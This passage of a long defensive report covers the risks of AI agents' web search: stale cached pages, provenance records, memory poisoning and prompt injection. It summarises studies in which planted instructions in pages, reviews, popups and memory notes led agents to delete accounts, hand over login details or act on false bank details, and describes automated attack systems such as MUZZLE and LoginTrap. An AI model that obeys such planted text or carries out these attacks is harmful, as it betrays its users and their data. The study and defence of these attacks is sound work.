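OpenAI says offline search does not cover the whole public web. A page may be missing because the site blocks crawlers, requires a login, or builds its content with scripts. New pages, rarely visited pages and pages deep inside a site may also be missing. Stored copies may be incomplete or old. OpenAI updates some pages quickly but does not promise to refresh any given page by a set time.

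How much stored-only search gives up depends on the question. OpenAI's developer guide illustrates cache-only search by asking when the Eiffel Tower opened to the public. Stored-only search gives up almost nothing on this question. The answer hasn't changed since 1889, so a three-year-old copy is as useful as a live page, and the answer appears on so many pages that a missing one hardly matters.

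Stored search is much less suited to finding today's room price. If no crawler saved the page for 12 June, the assistant can at least report that it found no price. If a snapshot contains one, the assistant may present a three-week-old price as current, and the user can't easily tell. The assistant could ask the user to paste the current price from the hotel's website. The user should find the page without using a link from the assistant, since an injection could have put the booking code in that link.

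For the third lookup, suppose a software company publishes a security notice about its library at eight in the morning, and a coding agent checks at two that afternoon whether the library is safe to install. If a crawler visits the notice page once a week, at a time unrelated to the notice, the chance that it has visited in those six hours is 6/168, or about 4%. With daily visits, the chance is 25%. The search will probably return older pages that describe the library as safe, and these may be well written and from the company itself.

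Offline search also can't reliably show what a page said at a particular time, because the results may not include when OpenAI saved the copy. OpenAI advises against using these results as audit evidence and recommends official documents or an archived record instead.

### When old information causes harm

The coding agent that missed the security notice might install the library, and an attacker could then exploit the flaw on the user's computer. The search would have contributed to a security failure even though it leaked nothing. An operator who switches to stored-only search to reduce one risk can increase another, especially if the agent acts on what it reads without asking anyone.

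The hotel assistant could do similar damage. If the hotel has moved its free cancellation deadline earlier, an assistant relying on an old page could cancel too late, leaving the user to pay for the room. An old page may also recommend a download from a domain whose registration has since lapsed. Someone else could have bought the domain, as researchers did with the one on Salesforce's list, and if another of the agent's tools has live access, the agent might fetch a malicious file from it.

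In these examples, the harm comes from acting now on an old fact. An operator can let the agent summarise stored pages freely but require a fresh check before it installs software, pays for something or relies on a deadline. A person can do the check, or a separate program can make a fixed request to an official source without using any text from the agent.

The operator can also keep important stored pages current by refreshing a fixed list of them on a schedule. For example, a program could copy the official security notices for certain software libraries every hour. This works well for sources the operator can list in advance, but it doesn't help with a question about a hotel that isn't on the list.

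### Settings that do less than their names suggest

A developer can set `external_web_access` to false and still get live searches. The older version of OpenAI's search tool, `web_search_preview`, is still available for existing applications, but OpenAI says it ignores the parameter and behaves as if live access were on. OpenAI's Chat Completions API offers no control over live access with its search models. Searches succeed in both cases, so the developer may not notice the problem.

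OpenAI's search tool can also draw on real-time feeds of sports, weather and financial data from other companies. OpenAI's explanation of cache-only mode does not mention these feeds. To check whether the feeds stay on in that mode, a developer can request the full list of sources with each answer and look for labels such as `oai-finance`.

Codex's web search defaults to live when a user starts it with `--yolo`, which also removes the sandbox and the approval requests. The deprecated `web_search_request` setting, which may remain in an old configuration file, also turns on live search if the newer `web_search` setting is missing. Once a user marks a project as trusted, the settings in its folder override the user's own, so a trusted project downloaded from a stranger could turn on live search.

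An organisation can prevent all this by putting `allowed_web_search_modes = ["cached"]` in a requirements file, which users cannot override. Bolin explains in *feat*, a note on the code change that added the rule, that it blocks live search even under `--yolo`. When a user's setting conflicts with such a rule, Codex switches to a permitted value and notifies the user, according to OpenAI's *Managed configuration*. In Vaughan's sample requirements file, the rule is named `web_search` instead, so an administrator who copies the file should check that it blocks live search.

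Even a working rule doesn't cover shell commands. Under `--yolo`, nothing in Codex stops the agent's commands from using the network, so a single command could send the booking code to the reviewer's server even while the search tool reads only from the cache. In Codex's normal mode, commands are offline until the user turns on network access. They can then contact any site unless the user also turns on `network_proxy`, which restricts them to named sites and is off by default.

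OpenAI marks Codex's network access with an "Elevated Risk" label. According to *Elevated Risk labels*, existing safeguards do not yet fully address the risks of features with this label, and OpenAI offers these features outside its standard warranties. The label is a useful warning on the settings screen, but it does not restrict anything.

Lockdown Mode doesn't help with any of this, because it doesn't affect Codex's network access. A person who signs in to both products with one account might reasonably expect the mode to cover both.

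OpenAI backs up cached search with several other controls when its own staff use Codex. *Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, 2026) describes a setup that allows only cached search and forbids running Codex without its sandbox. Commands can reach a short list of sites, and unfamiliar sites need approval. The rules block `pastebin.com`, where anyone can publish text. OpenAI also records tool results and blocked network requests so that its security team can investigate unusual activity.

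In this setup, an agent with cached search can still read some live content. One rule lets Codex view proposed code changes on GitHub from outside the sandbox without asking. Those requests go to GitHub's servers, and on a public project, anyone could have written the text that comes back. OpenAI's tradeoff is reasonable, since programmers need this information constantly and GitHub is a known company.

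### Checks for operators

Because a setting's name is weak evidence of what an agent can reach, an operator should test the whole agent before giving it private data:

1. List every route out of the agent's environment, including the shell, any browser, connected apps, MCP servers, and images in answers. Turn off the routes that the task does not need.
2. Set the search mode explicitly, even when the default is already right. Where the product allows it, enforce the mode with a rule that users can't change, and forbid full-access mode as well.
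3. Set up a web server, invent an address on it that contains a random string, and ask the agent to open it. The server's log should stay empty. Repeat the test with the random string in the host name, and check the name server's log too, because looking up a host name can also leak data.
4. Repeat the third check through each remaining route, including a shell command and an image. An empty log shows only that these particular calls stayed inside, so cutting the network connection is better wherever the operator controls the machine.
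5. Ask for a page that is not in the store, and for one that changed today. The agent should report that it could not find the first and warn that its copy of the second may be old. If it guesses, the operator should not let it act on stored pages without a fresh check.
6. Run the tests again after each update, and whenever someone connects a new app or tool.

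## How are the source and age of a stored result recorded?

An agent that reads a stored page needs to know where the page came from and how old it is, but the text often includes neither. Provenance is the record of where content came from, when it was fetched, and what has been done to it since. The software that fetches the page has to write this record at the time, because the website may change by the next day, and then nobody can check what it sent.

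### What the record should hold

| Field | What a reader can check |
|---|---|
| Address requested | Whether the crawler asked for the right page |
| Final address after redirects | Whether the text came from that page or from another one it forwards to |
| Time of fetch | How old the copy is, and whether it predates a known change |
| Who fetched it, and under what identity | Whether the server may have sent this visitor a special version |
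| Hash of the bytes | Whether the copy has changed since someone computed the hash |
| Later processing | Whether missing or odd text could come from conversion, translation or summarising |
| Trust label | Whether a stranger could have written the text |

The fetcher's identity includes its software name, location, language and any login. For example, a crawler that didn't identify itself as Claude would have saved a harmless version of Ayush Paul's website.

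A hash is a short string that a standard formula computes from the page's bytes. Changing one character of the page changes the hash, and with a modern formula there is no publicly known practical way to make a second page with the same hash.

### Two snapshots of a cancellation policy

Suppose the hotel guest booked on 10 May for a stay that starts on 12 June, and asks on 7 June whether cancelling is still free. The operator's store holds two snapshots of the hotel's policy.

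| | Older snapshot | Newer snapshot |
|---|---|---|
| Address requested | `hotel.example/cancel` | `hotel.example/cancel` |
| Final address | `hotel.example/cancel` | `hotel.example/cancel/saver` |
| Time of fetch | 26 April, 09:14 | 17 May, 09:10 |
| Fetched by | Operator's crawler, no login | Operator's crawler, no login |
| Hash begins | `3f9a` | `c07e` |
| Later processing | Converted to plain text | Converted to plain text |
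| Trust label | Untrusted | Untrusted |
| Text | Free until 48 hours before arrival | Free until 7 days before arrival |

The final addresses show that the newer request ended on a page for a cheaper "saver" rate, so both policies may be in force for different bookings. The assistant can check the confirmation email to see which rate the guest booked. If it was the standard rate, the guest may have until 10 June. From the text and dates alone, the assistant would probably conclude that the hotel had tightened its policy and that the guest missed the deadline two days ago.

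The different hashes provide little extra information, because a page with a rotating advertisement has a new hash on every visit. Both copies are at least three weeks old, so the agent still needs to recheck the deadline.

### Origin, alteration and truth

A good record can support the claim that a stored result came from a given address and, separately, that nobody has altered it since, but it can't establish that the content is true. A perfect copy of the hotel's own page may still give the wrong deadline because an employee mistyped it.

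Trusting the recorded source of a stored result usually means trusting the crawler's operator. HTTPS, the encrypted form of HTTP, lets a crawler check that it has reached the real holder of a host name, but doesn't give it proof to show anyone else. Both ends of the connection hold the secret keys that authenticate the data, so the crawler could have invented the response. A website could solve this by adding a digital signature, which only the holder of a secret key can make and anyone can check, but few sites sign their pages.

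A hash is evidence that a snapshot hasn't been altered only if no one who can change the snapshot can also change the hash. Someone who can edit both can replace the hash with one that matches the altered snapshot.

The trust label also doesn't show whether the text is true. *Utility Under Attack* (2026), a study of attacks on agent memory, assigns labels by the channel through which text arrived, so a note may be accurate or wrong whether it is labeled trusted or untrusted. This limits the labels but also makes them practical, since software can assign them without checking any facts.

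### What the existing standards prove

The web's caching standard helps a cache decide whether it can reuse a copy. To estimate a copy's age, the cache uses the server's `Date` header and the `Age` header described earlier:

current age = max(time received − `Date`, `Age` + delay) + time held since.

The cache estimates a copy's age on arrival in two ways, from the `Date` header and by adding the response delay to the `Age` header. It uses the larger estimate, in case a clock is wrong or an older cache on the way left out the `Age` header. For example, if a copy arrives with an `Age` of 600 seconds after a 2-second delay, and the `Date` header gives a smaller estimate, its age on arrival is 602 seconds. An hour later, its age is 602 + 3,600 = 4,202 seconds.

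A stored page can have a low age even if its text is old. Servers can give each version of a page an identifier called an ETag. When a copy expires, the cache sends the ETag back, and the server can reply that the version is still current. A policy written three years ago could therefore have an age of one minute. Servers can generate ETags by any method, so a match shows only that the server treats the two versions as equivalent.

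WARC, a file format that web archives use, is much closer to a full provenance record. A WARC file can hold the crawler's request and the server's complete response, along with the URL, the date, the server's IP address and a hash. Redirects appear as separate responses, so a reader can follow them to the final URL. If software later converts the page, the file can store the result as a separate record linked to the original. WARC has no standard field for a trust label. Anyone can write a WARC file with invented contents and matching hashes, so its reliability depends on who made and kept it.

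Memento, a 2013 internet standard, lets software ask an archive for a page as it was at a given time. The software sends the page's ordinary address and the desired date, and the archive returns a saved copy labelled with its date. The archive can also list the dates of all its copies of the page. A request to a public archive is itself a live request. The standard lets the archive choose which copy to return. If the assistant asked for the hotel's policy on 10 May, when the guest booked, an archive that picks the nearest date would return the snapshot from 17 May, a week too late. The assistant therefore has to check the date on the copy it receives.

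C2PA, from the Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity, attaches a signed statement to the file itself. The statement can describe how someone made and edited the file, and it includes a hash of the contents. A reader's software recomputes the hash and checks the signature. This shows who signed the statement and that the file has not changed since, so the reader doesn't have to trust whoever stored it. But C2PA is mainly for images, video, audio and documents, and a crawler that saves only a page's text will usually discard the statement. A correctly signed file could also be out of date or unrepresentative, such as a ten-year-old photograph of the hotel's best room.

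### What agent products return

Agent products usually return much less information than a WARC file holds. OpenAI's search tool returns the address, title and location of each source it cites, along with the full source list mentioned earlier. Developers must display the citations as clickable links.

These links identify a page but not a version of it. If the assistant answered from the April snapshot and the guest clicks the citation in June, the link will open the June page. The guest may find a different policy and conclude that the assistant made up the first one. The fetch time would help explain the difference, but OpenAI's offline search may leave it out. When Anthropic introduced its fetch tool in 2025, each result came with a retrieval time.

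A research system from October 2026 goes further by giving every version of a page its own address. *WEB$HELL* (Kim, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes an interface between an agent and the web. It fetches the top search results, uses fixed rules to turn each page into files of text, tables, links and available actions, and stores the files for the rest of the task. If the agent clicks a button and the page changes, the interface saves the new state under a new address and reports which action caused the change. The earlier state stays available for reading only.

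The interface also separates reading a saved page from acting on a live one. Its list of stored pages marks the most recently used open page as `[active]` and other open pages as `[live]`. An agent can read an unmarked page, but doing so does not return the browser to that state. If the agent tries to press a button on a saved page whose browser tab has closed, the interface returns a message saying that the agent cannot act from there. With this system, the hotel assistant could compare the standard and saver policies as two saved states, each with its own address, and would be less likely to mix them up.

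Kim and colleagues compared the system with three alternatives on six benchmarks, using GPT-5.6 Luna throughout. The system scored best on all six, though the margins varied a lot.

| Benchmark | Type of task | New system | Best alternative |
|---|---|---|---|
| WideSearch | Collecting facts into tables | 0.782 | 0.745 |
| SealQA | Questions with conflicting search results | 0.720 | 0.665 |
| WebArena-Verified | Operating copies of websites | 0.679 | 0.578 |
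| WebWalkerQA | Finding answers within a website | 0.671 | 0.636 |
| DeepResearchBench | Writing research reports | 0.534 | 0.528 |
| DeepWeb-Bench (out of 100) | Calculating from many sources | 31.11 | 28.37 |

These scores cover the whole interface, so they don't show how much the separate addresses contributed. The closest evidence comes from a test that added as many as 400 irrelevant pages to the store. Accuracy and cost stayed largely stable, while the cost of one alternative more than doubled. Kim and colleagues credit the short, reusable page addresses for this stability. Their experiments measured task performance and cost but didn't test the system as a security measure.

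### How a page becomes the agent's own memory

An agent can lose even a good record of a stored page's source and age when it takes notes. Many agents keep a memory between conversations. At the end of a session, a language model condenses what happened into short notes, and later sessions load some of them into the context. By then the original page is gone. If the software saved only the text of the note, the agent can't tell a stranger's claim from something the user said.

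*Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which a web page contains an instruction for the agent to resume a certain workflow when setting up monitoring. The summarising model may save this instruction as "user workflow memory", which makes it look like the user's own habit.

This happens often even when nobody is attacking. For *When Memory Becomes Authority*, Zhan, Guo and colleagues (2026) wrote 350 pairs of conversation histories to measure it. In one history of each pair, the user stated a fact or preference. In the other, the same claim came from an assistant, a tool or an outsider, and the user never adopted it. The researchers tested seven models with seven ways of writing notes. In 48 of the 49 combinations, some notes gave a claim more authority than its source justified. The remaining combination avoided the error only by saving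 none of the claims that the user had not adopted. On average, the models kept 26% of those claims, and about two thirds of the ones they kept gained authority.

When the researchers required the model to save the claim, 55.8% of the claims gained authority. The share fell to 9.9% when they also told the model to preserve who had made the claim, how certain the source was, and whether the user had agreed.

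Notes can also lose the record of how old they are. *Manufactured Confidence* (Kwon, 2026) tested two memory products, mem0 and LangMem, on conversations that mentioned early on that Alice was an administrator. She later lost that role in a session the agent never saw. Both products stored her promotion as a plain fact, with nothing to mark it as old. An agent using these notes to control access wrongly granted 69% of Alice's requests with one product and 75% with the other. When the correction appeared in the same conversation, both products updated the note and the agent granted none. The test was small, with 16 requests per condition.

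Sometimes an ordinary programming mistake removes part of a record. *How Much Should an Agent Remember?* (2026) describes a system that merged related notes and rebuilt their records from a fixed list of fields. It silently dropped anything not on the list, including a tag that another team relied on. An agent's own words can also come back to it under a new source. This happened when online shops turned agents' searches into public pages. A crawler's record of such a page would correctly name the shop as the source but leave out the agent that supplied the words.

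### Experiments with poisoned memory

An attacker can exploit this loss of provenance by planting text that the agent saves in one session and acts on in another. *MemoryDojo* (Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues, 2026) tested how far a single planted text could spread. Agents worked through sequences of office, travel, banking and messaging tasks. The researchers added a malicious instruction to one tool result in the first task and did not intervene again. Each later task started with only what the memory system retrieved, so the instruction could affect those tasks only through memory.

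The table covers 93 sequences in which every task was of the same type. It shows how often the agent carried out the attacker's goal in at least one later task. For the last column, a language model first improved the planted text by practising against that memory system.

| Memory system | Plain attack | Improved attack |
|---|---|---|
| A-MEM | 45.7% | 71.0% |
| Memora | 38.7% | 66.7% |
| Graphiti | 24.7% | 30.1% |
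| Letta | 16.7% | 50.5% |
| Mem0 | 14.5% | 39.8% |

An agent that followed the planted instruction might also save a note about what it had done, and that note contained the instruction too. With A-MEM and the plain attack, about 40% of the later tasks that retrieved the instruction received at least one such copy, so deleting the original note would not have been enough to remove the instruction.

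Memory systems that already held about 50 ordinary conversations were harder to poison, because the planted note competed with more stored material. In these systems, the attacker's goal appeared in at most 5.3% of later tasks. But the attack needs to succeed only once, and with Memora the goal still appeared at least once in 45% of the sequences.

How an agent reads its memory also affects how often a malicious note influences it. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (Dash, Ge and colleagues, 2026) compared Hermes, which loads its saved notes automatically at the start of each session, with OpenClaw, which searches its memory only when the agent decides to. Once a malicious note was in memory, it influenced a later session 65% of the time in Hermes and 17% of the time in OpenClaw.

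Showing an agent where each note came from can make it less likely to act on false information. *Ask, Forget, Repair* (Motwani, 2026) tested this with six models acting as an office assistant over 60 simulated sessions. Some documents contained planted details, such as a false bank account for a supplier, and each model faced 150 of these. When notes had no recorded source, the planted details led to a wrong action in 2% to 93% of cases across the six models. When the model could see a label marking the note as untrusted, the rate fell to 1% or less for four models. It was still 15% for GPT-6.1 Terra and 67% for Llama 4 Maverick, so a label protects an agent only if the model heeds it or other software enforces it. The planted texts were simple, and an attacker who knew about the labels would probably succeed more often.

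### A note inherits its least trusted source

These failures suggest a rule for anything an agent writes down: a derived note inherits the trust label of its least trusted source. Xu and colleagues state it for each claim *q* in a note. If supp(*q*) is the set of sources that support the claim, then

auth(*q*) ≤ min { auth(*o*) : *o* in supp(*q*) },

where auth is the level of authority. Their levels run from unknown sources at the bottom, through external content, trusted tools and the user's history, to facts the user has confirmed and finally the system's own settings.

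Suppose the hotel assistant writes, "The user can cancel for free until 10 June." The arrival date came from the user, but the 48-hour policy came from a web page, so the note is labelled as external content even though it sounds like a fact about the user. The software keeps the label outside the note's text, where the model can't change it, so an attacker can't alter the label by writing "confirmed by the user" on the page.

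The other provenance fields should carry over too. *From Lossy to Verified* (2026) describes a memory system in which an updated note keeps links to the sources of both the old version and the new evidence. In Motwani's system, a merged note keeps all its sources and the earliest of their expiry dates. Keeping the sources makes it possible to clean up after an attack. When Motwani tried to remove everything that came from the malicious documents, none of the saved planted items remained in memories with provenance labels, while 67% to 93% remained in memories without them, depending on the model.

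The drawback is that the "untrusted" label spreads. If each source independently has a 20% chance of being untrusted, a note based on *k* sources stays trusted with probability 0.8ᵏ, which is 33% for five sources and 11% for ten. Notes based on other notes have even more sources, so eventually almost everything in memory is labelled untrusted and the label no longer helps with decisions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls this "label explosion".

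In the version of Motwani's experiment with labels but no enforcement, the software merged notes on the same topic. The user's answer to a question about a supplier's account was sometimes merged with an untrusted note and became untrusted itself, so the more careful models asked again. Nearly half of the questions from the three models that never acted on an untrusted note were about something the user had already told them. Keeping trusted and untrusted notes apart during merging stopped the repeated questions.

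The simplest way to track sources is to give every note from a session the label of the least trusted thing the agent read in that session. Zhan and colleagues tried a method like this, and it cut task success to about 5%, according to Motwani. Labelling each note by the sources that support it keeps far more notes usable, but the software then has to identify those sources correctly. *AgentKernel* (2026), which labels individual notes, warns that an attacker could write text that blurs the boundary between sources, so that a note gets a higher label than it should, a risk that labelling the whole session avoids.

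Dividing the work among several agents slows the spread, because an agent that never receives the untrusted text can stay trusted. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated this in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, using labels for sensitive data, which spread in the same way. Labels spread less when agents passed information directly to the agents that needed it, and when a few agents handled all the sensitive tools. No arrangement stopped the spread, because the simulation had no way to remove a label.

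A practical system therefore needs a safe way to raise a label. Xu and colleagues allow this only when the system has recorded an approval for that user, type of action and target. If the guest confirms the 10 June deadline with the hotel and tells the assistant, the software can store it as a fact from the user. The guest's approval would not cover anything else on the hotel's page.

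## What can retrieved content make an agent do?

A stranger's text can mislead an agent with false information or redirect it with instructions. The damage depends largely on the agent's other tools.

### Why a model can mistake text for instructions

In most software, the programmer decides in advance which input counts as an instruction. A hotel's booking system, for example, saves a guest's review in its database regardless of its content. A language model has no such separation between instructions and other input. Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) explain in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* that many applications combine the developer's instructions with outside text in a single context and cannot reliably keep the two separate.

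Developers can mark where a tool's result begins and ends, and train models to give the marked text less authority than the user's request. This helps, but it is a learned behavior that nothing in the model enforces.

An agent can't ignore every instruction on a web page, because some are part of the task. If a user plans to arrive late at a hotel, and the hotel's page says that late guests must email the front desk, the agent should send the email. It has to judge whether each instruction serves the user's purpose, and an attacker can write an instruction that appears to serve it.

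### Four kinds of harm

| Harm | Example | What it needs besides a stored read |
|---|---|---|
| Wrong answer | The assistant praises a bad hotel because hidden text on the page asked for praise | Nothing |
| Disclosed secret | The reviewer receives the booking code | A way to send data out, such as a live page fetch, an email tool or an image in the answer |
| Unwanted action | The assistant cancels the booking, buys something or sends a message | A tool that can change something |
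| Unsafe code | A coding agent runs a harmful command it found on a page | A tool that can run code |

A wrong answer can be serious even if the agent has no other tools, because the user may act on it. If the agent repeats a scammer's phone number as a hotel's, the user may call it and read out their booking code.

An agent always needs some route out of the operator's systems to disclose a secret to an outsider, buy something or message a stranger. But it can delete a file on the operator's own computer without making a live request, and stored-only search does nothing to prevent that.

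Unsafe code can also do harm offline, because a stored page might contain a complete command that could destroy local files. A live connection allows more harm, because the agent can then download a larger program or send data to the attacker. The pseudonymous security tester veganmosfet (2026) reports in *The Prompt Injection Quest to RCE* that two recent models running without approval requests downloaded and ran untrusted code when asked only to summarise a software project.

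### How common injections are on real websites

Khodayari and colleagues searched about half of the October 2025 collection of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injections. Their sample covered 1.2 billion addresses on 24.8 million hosts. They then separated real instructions to AI systems from tutorials and news articles that merely quoted them.

The researchers confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or about one page in 124,000. These pages belonged to only 285 hosts. They describe the count as a lower bound. They found another 3,312 injections through Censys and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected servers. They used this second set to study what injections look like, not how common they are.

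In the Common Crawl sample, website operators had written 80.6% of the injections themselves. Another 17.6% were in material that other people had placed on the site, such as job advertisements. Only 1.8% were in comments and similar user posts, so injections like the malicious hotel review are uncommon.

The next table covers all 15,387 injections from the three sources. Some had more than one aim.

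| Apparent aim | Injections |
|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system, usually by making it write nonsense | 8,894 |
| Stop AI systems from reusing personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 |
| Find out whether a visitor is an AI | 3,096 |
| Replace the system's task, for no clear purpose | 2,632 |
| Promote a product, source or job candidate, or obtain good reviews | 1,521 |
| Extract secrets or the system's hidden instructions | 13 |

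Many of these injections seem to come from website owners who want to keep automated visitors away, rather than from criminals trying to rob users. But 157 of the disruptive ones were meant to make an agent run commands, some of which would delete files or database tables. Agents that can run code would be the most exposed to these.

The small number of attempted thefts is weaker evidence about attacks on particular users or companies. Common Crawl may miss much of the content behind logins, where agents often handle private data. The phrase search also missed unfamiliar wordings, many injections in other languages, and text inside images. A careful thief would probably avoid well-known phrases. Khodayari and colleagues also cite a Google analysis that found a 32% rise in malicious injections between November 2025 and February 2026.

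Users would rarely notice these injections by looking at the page. About 70% were in places that a browser doesn't display, such as HTTP headers and comments in the page's code. The rest were often hidden too, for example in tiny text or text in the same colour as the background.

### How often models followed them

To see whether these injections work, Khodayari and colleagues chose 100 and asked 13 models to summarise the pages that contained them. Each model received each page in four formats, which made 5,200 runs. The models followed the injected instruction in 81 runs, or 1.6%.

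| Format | Followed the injection | Failed with an error |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text | 3.9% | 0.7% |
| Page code (HTML) | 1.1% | 20.3% |
| Structured outline of the displayed page | 1.1% | 3.5% |
| Complete server response, including headers | 0.2% | 25.8% |

Page code and complete responses were often too long for a model to process, which partly explains their low rates. Plain text and the structured outline make the fairest comparison, since few of those runs failed. Khodayari and colleagues think plain text is riskier because it removes the signs that a sentence was hidden, so the sentence looks like an ordinary part of the page.

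In stored search, a crawler may convert pages to plain text before saving them. The conversion shortens pages, so they take less compute to process, and removes the headers, which contained about half of the injections. But it also makes any hidden sentence that remains harder for the model to recognise.

Small models followed 4.2% of the injections overall and 8.0% in plain text. The commercial models whose size is not public followed 0.6% overall, or five in 800 runs, and pointed out the injection in a quarter of their runs. In six runs, a model identified the injected instruction and followed it anyway.

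The models in this test only wrote summaries, so the results measure how often an injection changes an answer. An agent with tools might do better or worse.

### Attacks that adapt to the agent

Most of the injections Khodayari and colleagues found were fixed texts, and 54 templates accounted for 95% of them. An attacker who studies a particular agent can write much more effective injections. *MUZZLE* (Syros, Kerschbaumer and colleagues, 2026) presents a system that automates this.

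MUZZLE monitors the agent during an ordinary task and records which parts of each page influence it. It then picks a promising place for an injection, such as a comment, writes an instruction, and revises it based on how the agent responds. It reruns the whole task to test the attack and, if the attack fails, tries another wording or place. An attacker would need a copy of the agent to test against, but could post the finished text from an ordinary user account.

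The researchers used a simulated web with a code-hosting site, a forum, a classified ads site and a database management tool. They tested the BrowserUse agent, running on GPT-4o, five times for each goal. The table shows how many times the agent adopted the attacker's goal and how many times it completed that goal.

| Where the agent was working | Attacker's goal | Adopted | Completed |
|---|---|---|---|
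| Code hosting | Delete the project | 3 | 1 |
| Code hosting | Give an outsider access to the project | 4 | 2 |
| Code hosting | Set up automatic reports to the attacker | 4 | 0 |
| Code hosting | Delete the user's account on the forum | 4 | 1 |
| Forum | Delete the user's account | 5 | 1 |
| Forum | Post a scam link | 3 | 2 |
| Forum | Steal the user's login details | 4 | 4 |
| Classified ads | Delete the user's account | 3 | 1 |
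| Classified ads | Remove a competitor's listing | 4 | 3 |
| Classified ads | Change the account's email address | 4 | 1 |
| Classified ads | Delete a table in the database tool | 5 | 2 |

The agent adopted the attacker's goal in 43 of these 55 runs but completed it in only 18. GPT-4o often started on the attacker's task and then returned to the user's. In two of the cases, the injection on one site led the agent to log in to another site with the user's stored login details and destroy something there.

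Attacks aimed at stealing the login details worked best. GPT-4o and GPT-4.1 tended not to reveal them in response to a direct request in an injection, but the agent filled in a fake login page when the injection described it as a routine check.

Syros and colleagues also tried two other models on the forum and another agent design on the code-hosting site. Including these tests, 44 of 100 runs ended in a complete attack. GPT-4.1 deleted the user's forum account in four of five runs, compared with one of five for GPT-4o, although GPT-4.1 is the newer model.

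The other design, Agent-E, completed seven of 15 attacks on the code-hosting site, while BrowserUse completed three. Agent-E has a planner that hands each step to a second component, which operates the browser and reports only whether the step succeeded. Dividing work between agents can keep untrusted text away from some of them, but here it also kept the planner from detecting that an injection had taken over the second component.

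In a separate comparison, MUZZLE's attacks succeeded in 86.7% of runs, while a fixed template from an older benchmark succeeded in 20%. The comparison favours MUZZLE because the researchers chose MUZZLE attacks that had already worked at least once. It still shows that an agent that resists a standard test can fail against an attacker who has practised on that agent.

### Fake login pages

In *LoginTrap*, Guo, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested an attacker who knows nothing about the user's task, the model or the agent's design. The attacker copies a real web page and adds a popup that makes logging in seem necessary. The popup's button leads to a fake login page that asks for sensitive information. Software writes the popup to suit each page and tries it on two language models first.

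The test used copies of 80 real pages and 1,175 ordinary tasks, such as searching for information or comparing products. The agents had made-up personal details as background. BrowserUse, run on GPT-4o, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Sonnet 4 and DeepSeek-V3.2, clicked through to the fake login page in 93% of tasks on average and entered sensitive information in 86%. For every model, each of the 80 pages worked at least once in nine attempts.

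The success rate depended somewhat on the agent's design, ranging from 68% to 89% across three designs running on GPT-4o. Agents that reached the login page without giving up any information had mostly left the form incomplete, stopped early or gone back to the original task. Guo and colleagues attribute this to interruptions, not to the agents recognising that the page was fake. They suggest that it may therefore be easier to steal information in this way from agents that are better at finishing tasks.

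The 86% rate applies only to agents already on the attacker's copy of a page, and the attacker still has to get them there. The rate also depends on the agent having the sensitive details in its context. Withholding passwords from an agent that only needs to compare hotel prices would remove much of the risk.

The worst results in both studies depend on live tools. A stored page can contain the popup or the malicious comment, and the agent may adopt the attacker's goal after reading it. But the agent can't submit a form through a saved copy, so it couldn't send the login details unless it also had a live browser or another way to transmit them.

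### Success rates for newer models

Neither study tested the strongest models of 2026, which resist injections much better in some settings. VentureBeat reports results for Claude Opus 4.6, from February, and The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports results for Opus 5 and other Claude models. Gray Swan, a security company, designed one of the tests.

| Model | Test | Successful attacks |
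|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding, 200 attempts, no added safeguards | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a screen, one attempt, no added safeguards | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a screen, 200 attempts, no added safeguards | 78.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a screen, 200 attempts, with safeguards | 57.1% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan's test, 15 attempts | 5.5% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Gray Swan's test, 15 attempts | 2.8% |
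| Claude Mythos 5 | Gray Swan's test, 15 attempts | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan's test, 15 attempts | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 129 browser scenarios | 0% |

A single attack success rate can be misleading. Opus 4.6 resisted every attack in one setting, but in another, attacks usually succeeded once the attacker had made enough attempts. If each attempt on the screen-operating agent had an independent 17.8% chance of success, the attacker's overall success rate would have exceeded 78.6% by the eighth attempt. The actual rate rose more slowly, which suggests that some scenarios were much harder to attack than others.

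Attack success rates also vary between developers. Wizwand's *Indirect Prompt Injection on LivePI Total*, a leaderboard from May, lists rates of 10.7% for Claude Opus 4.6, 16.6% for Kimi K2.5, 27.2% for GPT-5.3-Codex, 27.8% for GLM-5 and 29.6% for Gemini 3.1 Pro. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 resists attacks in the user's own messages well, but attacks that arrive through tools and outside content succeed more often, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). The results for tools and outside content are the relevant ones for an operator whose agent reads web pages.

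People reading the same system card can disagree. Anthropic emphasised that Mythos 5 had the best score so far on Gray Swan's test and was otherwise broadly comparable to earlier models. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* reports that the model and its safeguards had become less effective at blocking prompt injections, and criticises the card for playing this down. Both descriptions may be accurate, since a model can improve on one test while getting worse on another.

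Opus 5's perfect browser result is a large improvement and makes it plausible that a well-protected browser agent would withstand most injections now on the web, but it doesn't rule out a new kind of attack succeeding. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) similarly notes that the absence of observed failures in OpenAI's alignment tests does not establish reliability in other settings.

The Opus 5 figures are also no longer the newest. *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a commentary on Anthropic's September system card, reports that resistance to injections in outside content improved further. In *Fable and Mythos 5.2*, Mowshowitz (2026) discusses the system card for the models that followed in November. That card also covers prompt injection.

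### Harmful pages without instructions

A page can cause harm without containing any instruction. Suppose someone sets up a convincing fake website for the hotel that lists a different bank account for deposits. If the user asks the assistant to pay the deposit, it may send the money to the wrong person. Motwani's false supplier accounts posed the same kind of threat. A model that never follows injected instructions could still make this mistake, because the instruction to pay came from the user.

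Software that looks for injections would also find nothing suspicious in a page that makes its claims without addressing an AI. Khodayari and colleagues counted 542 injections that told AI systems to treat a page as the authority on its subject and cite it. Their search would not have counted those pages if they had only claimed to be authoritative.

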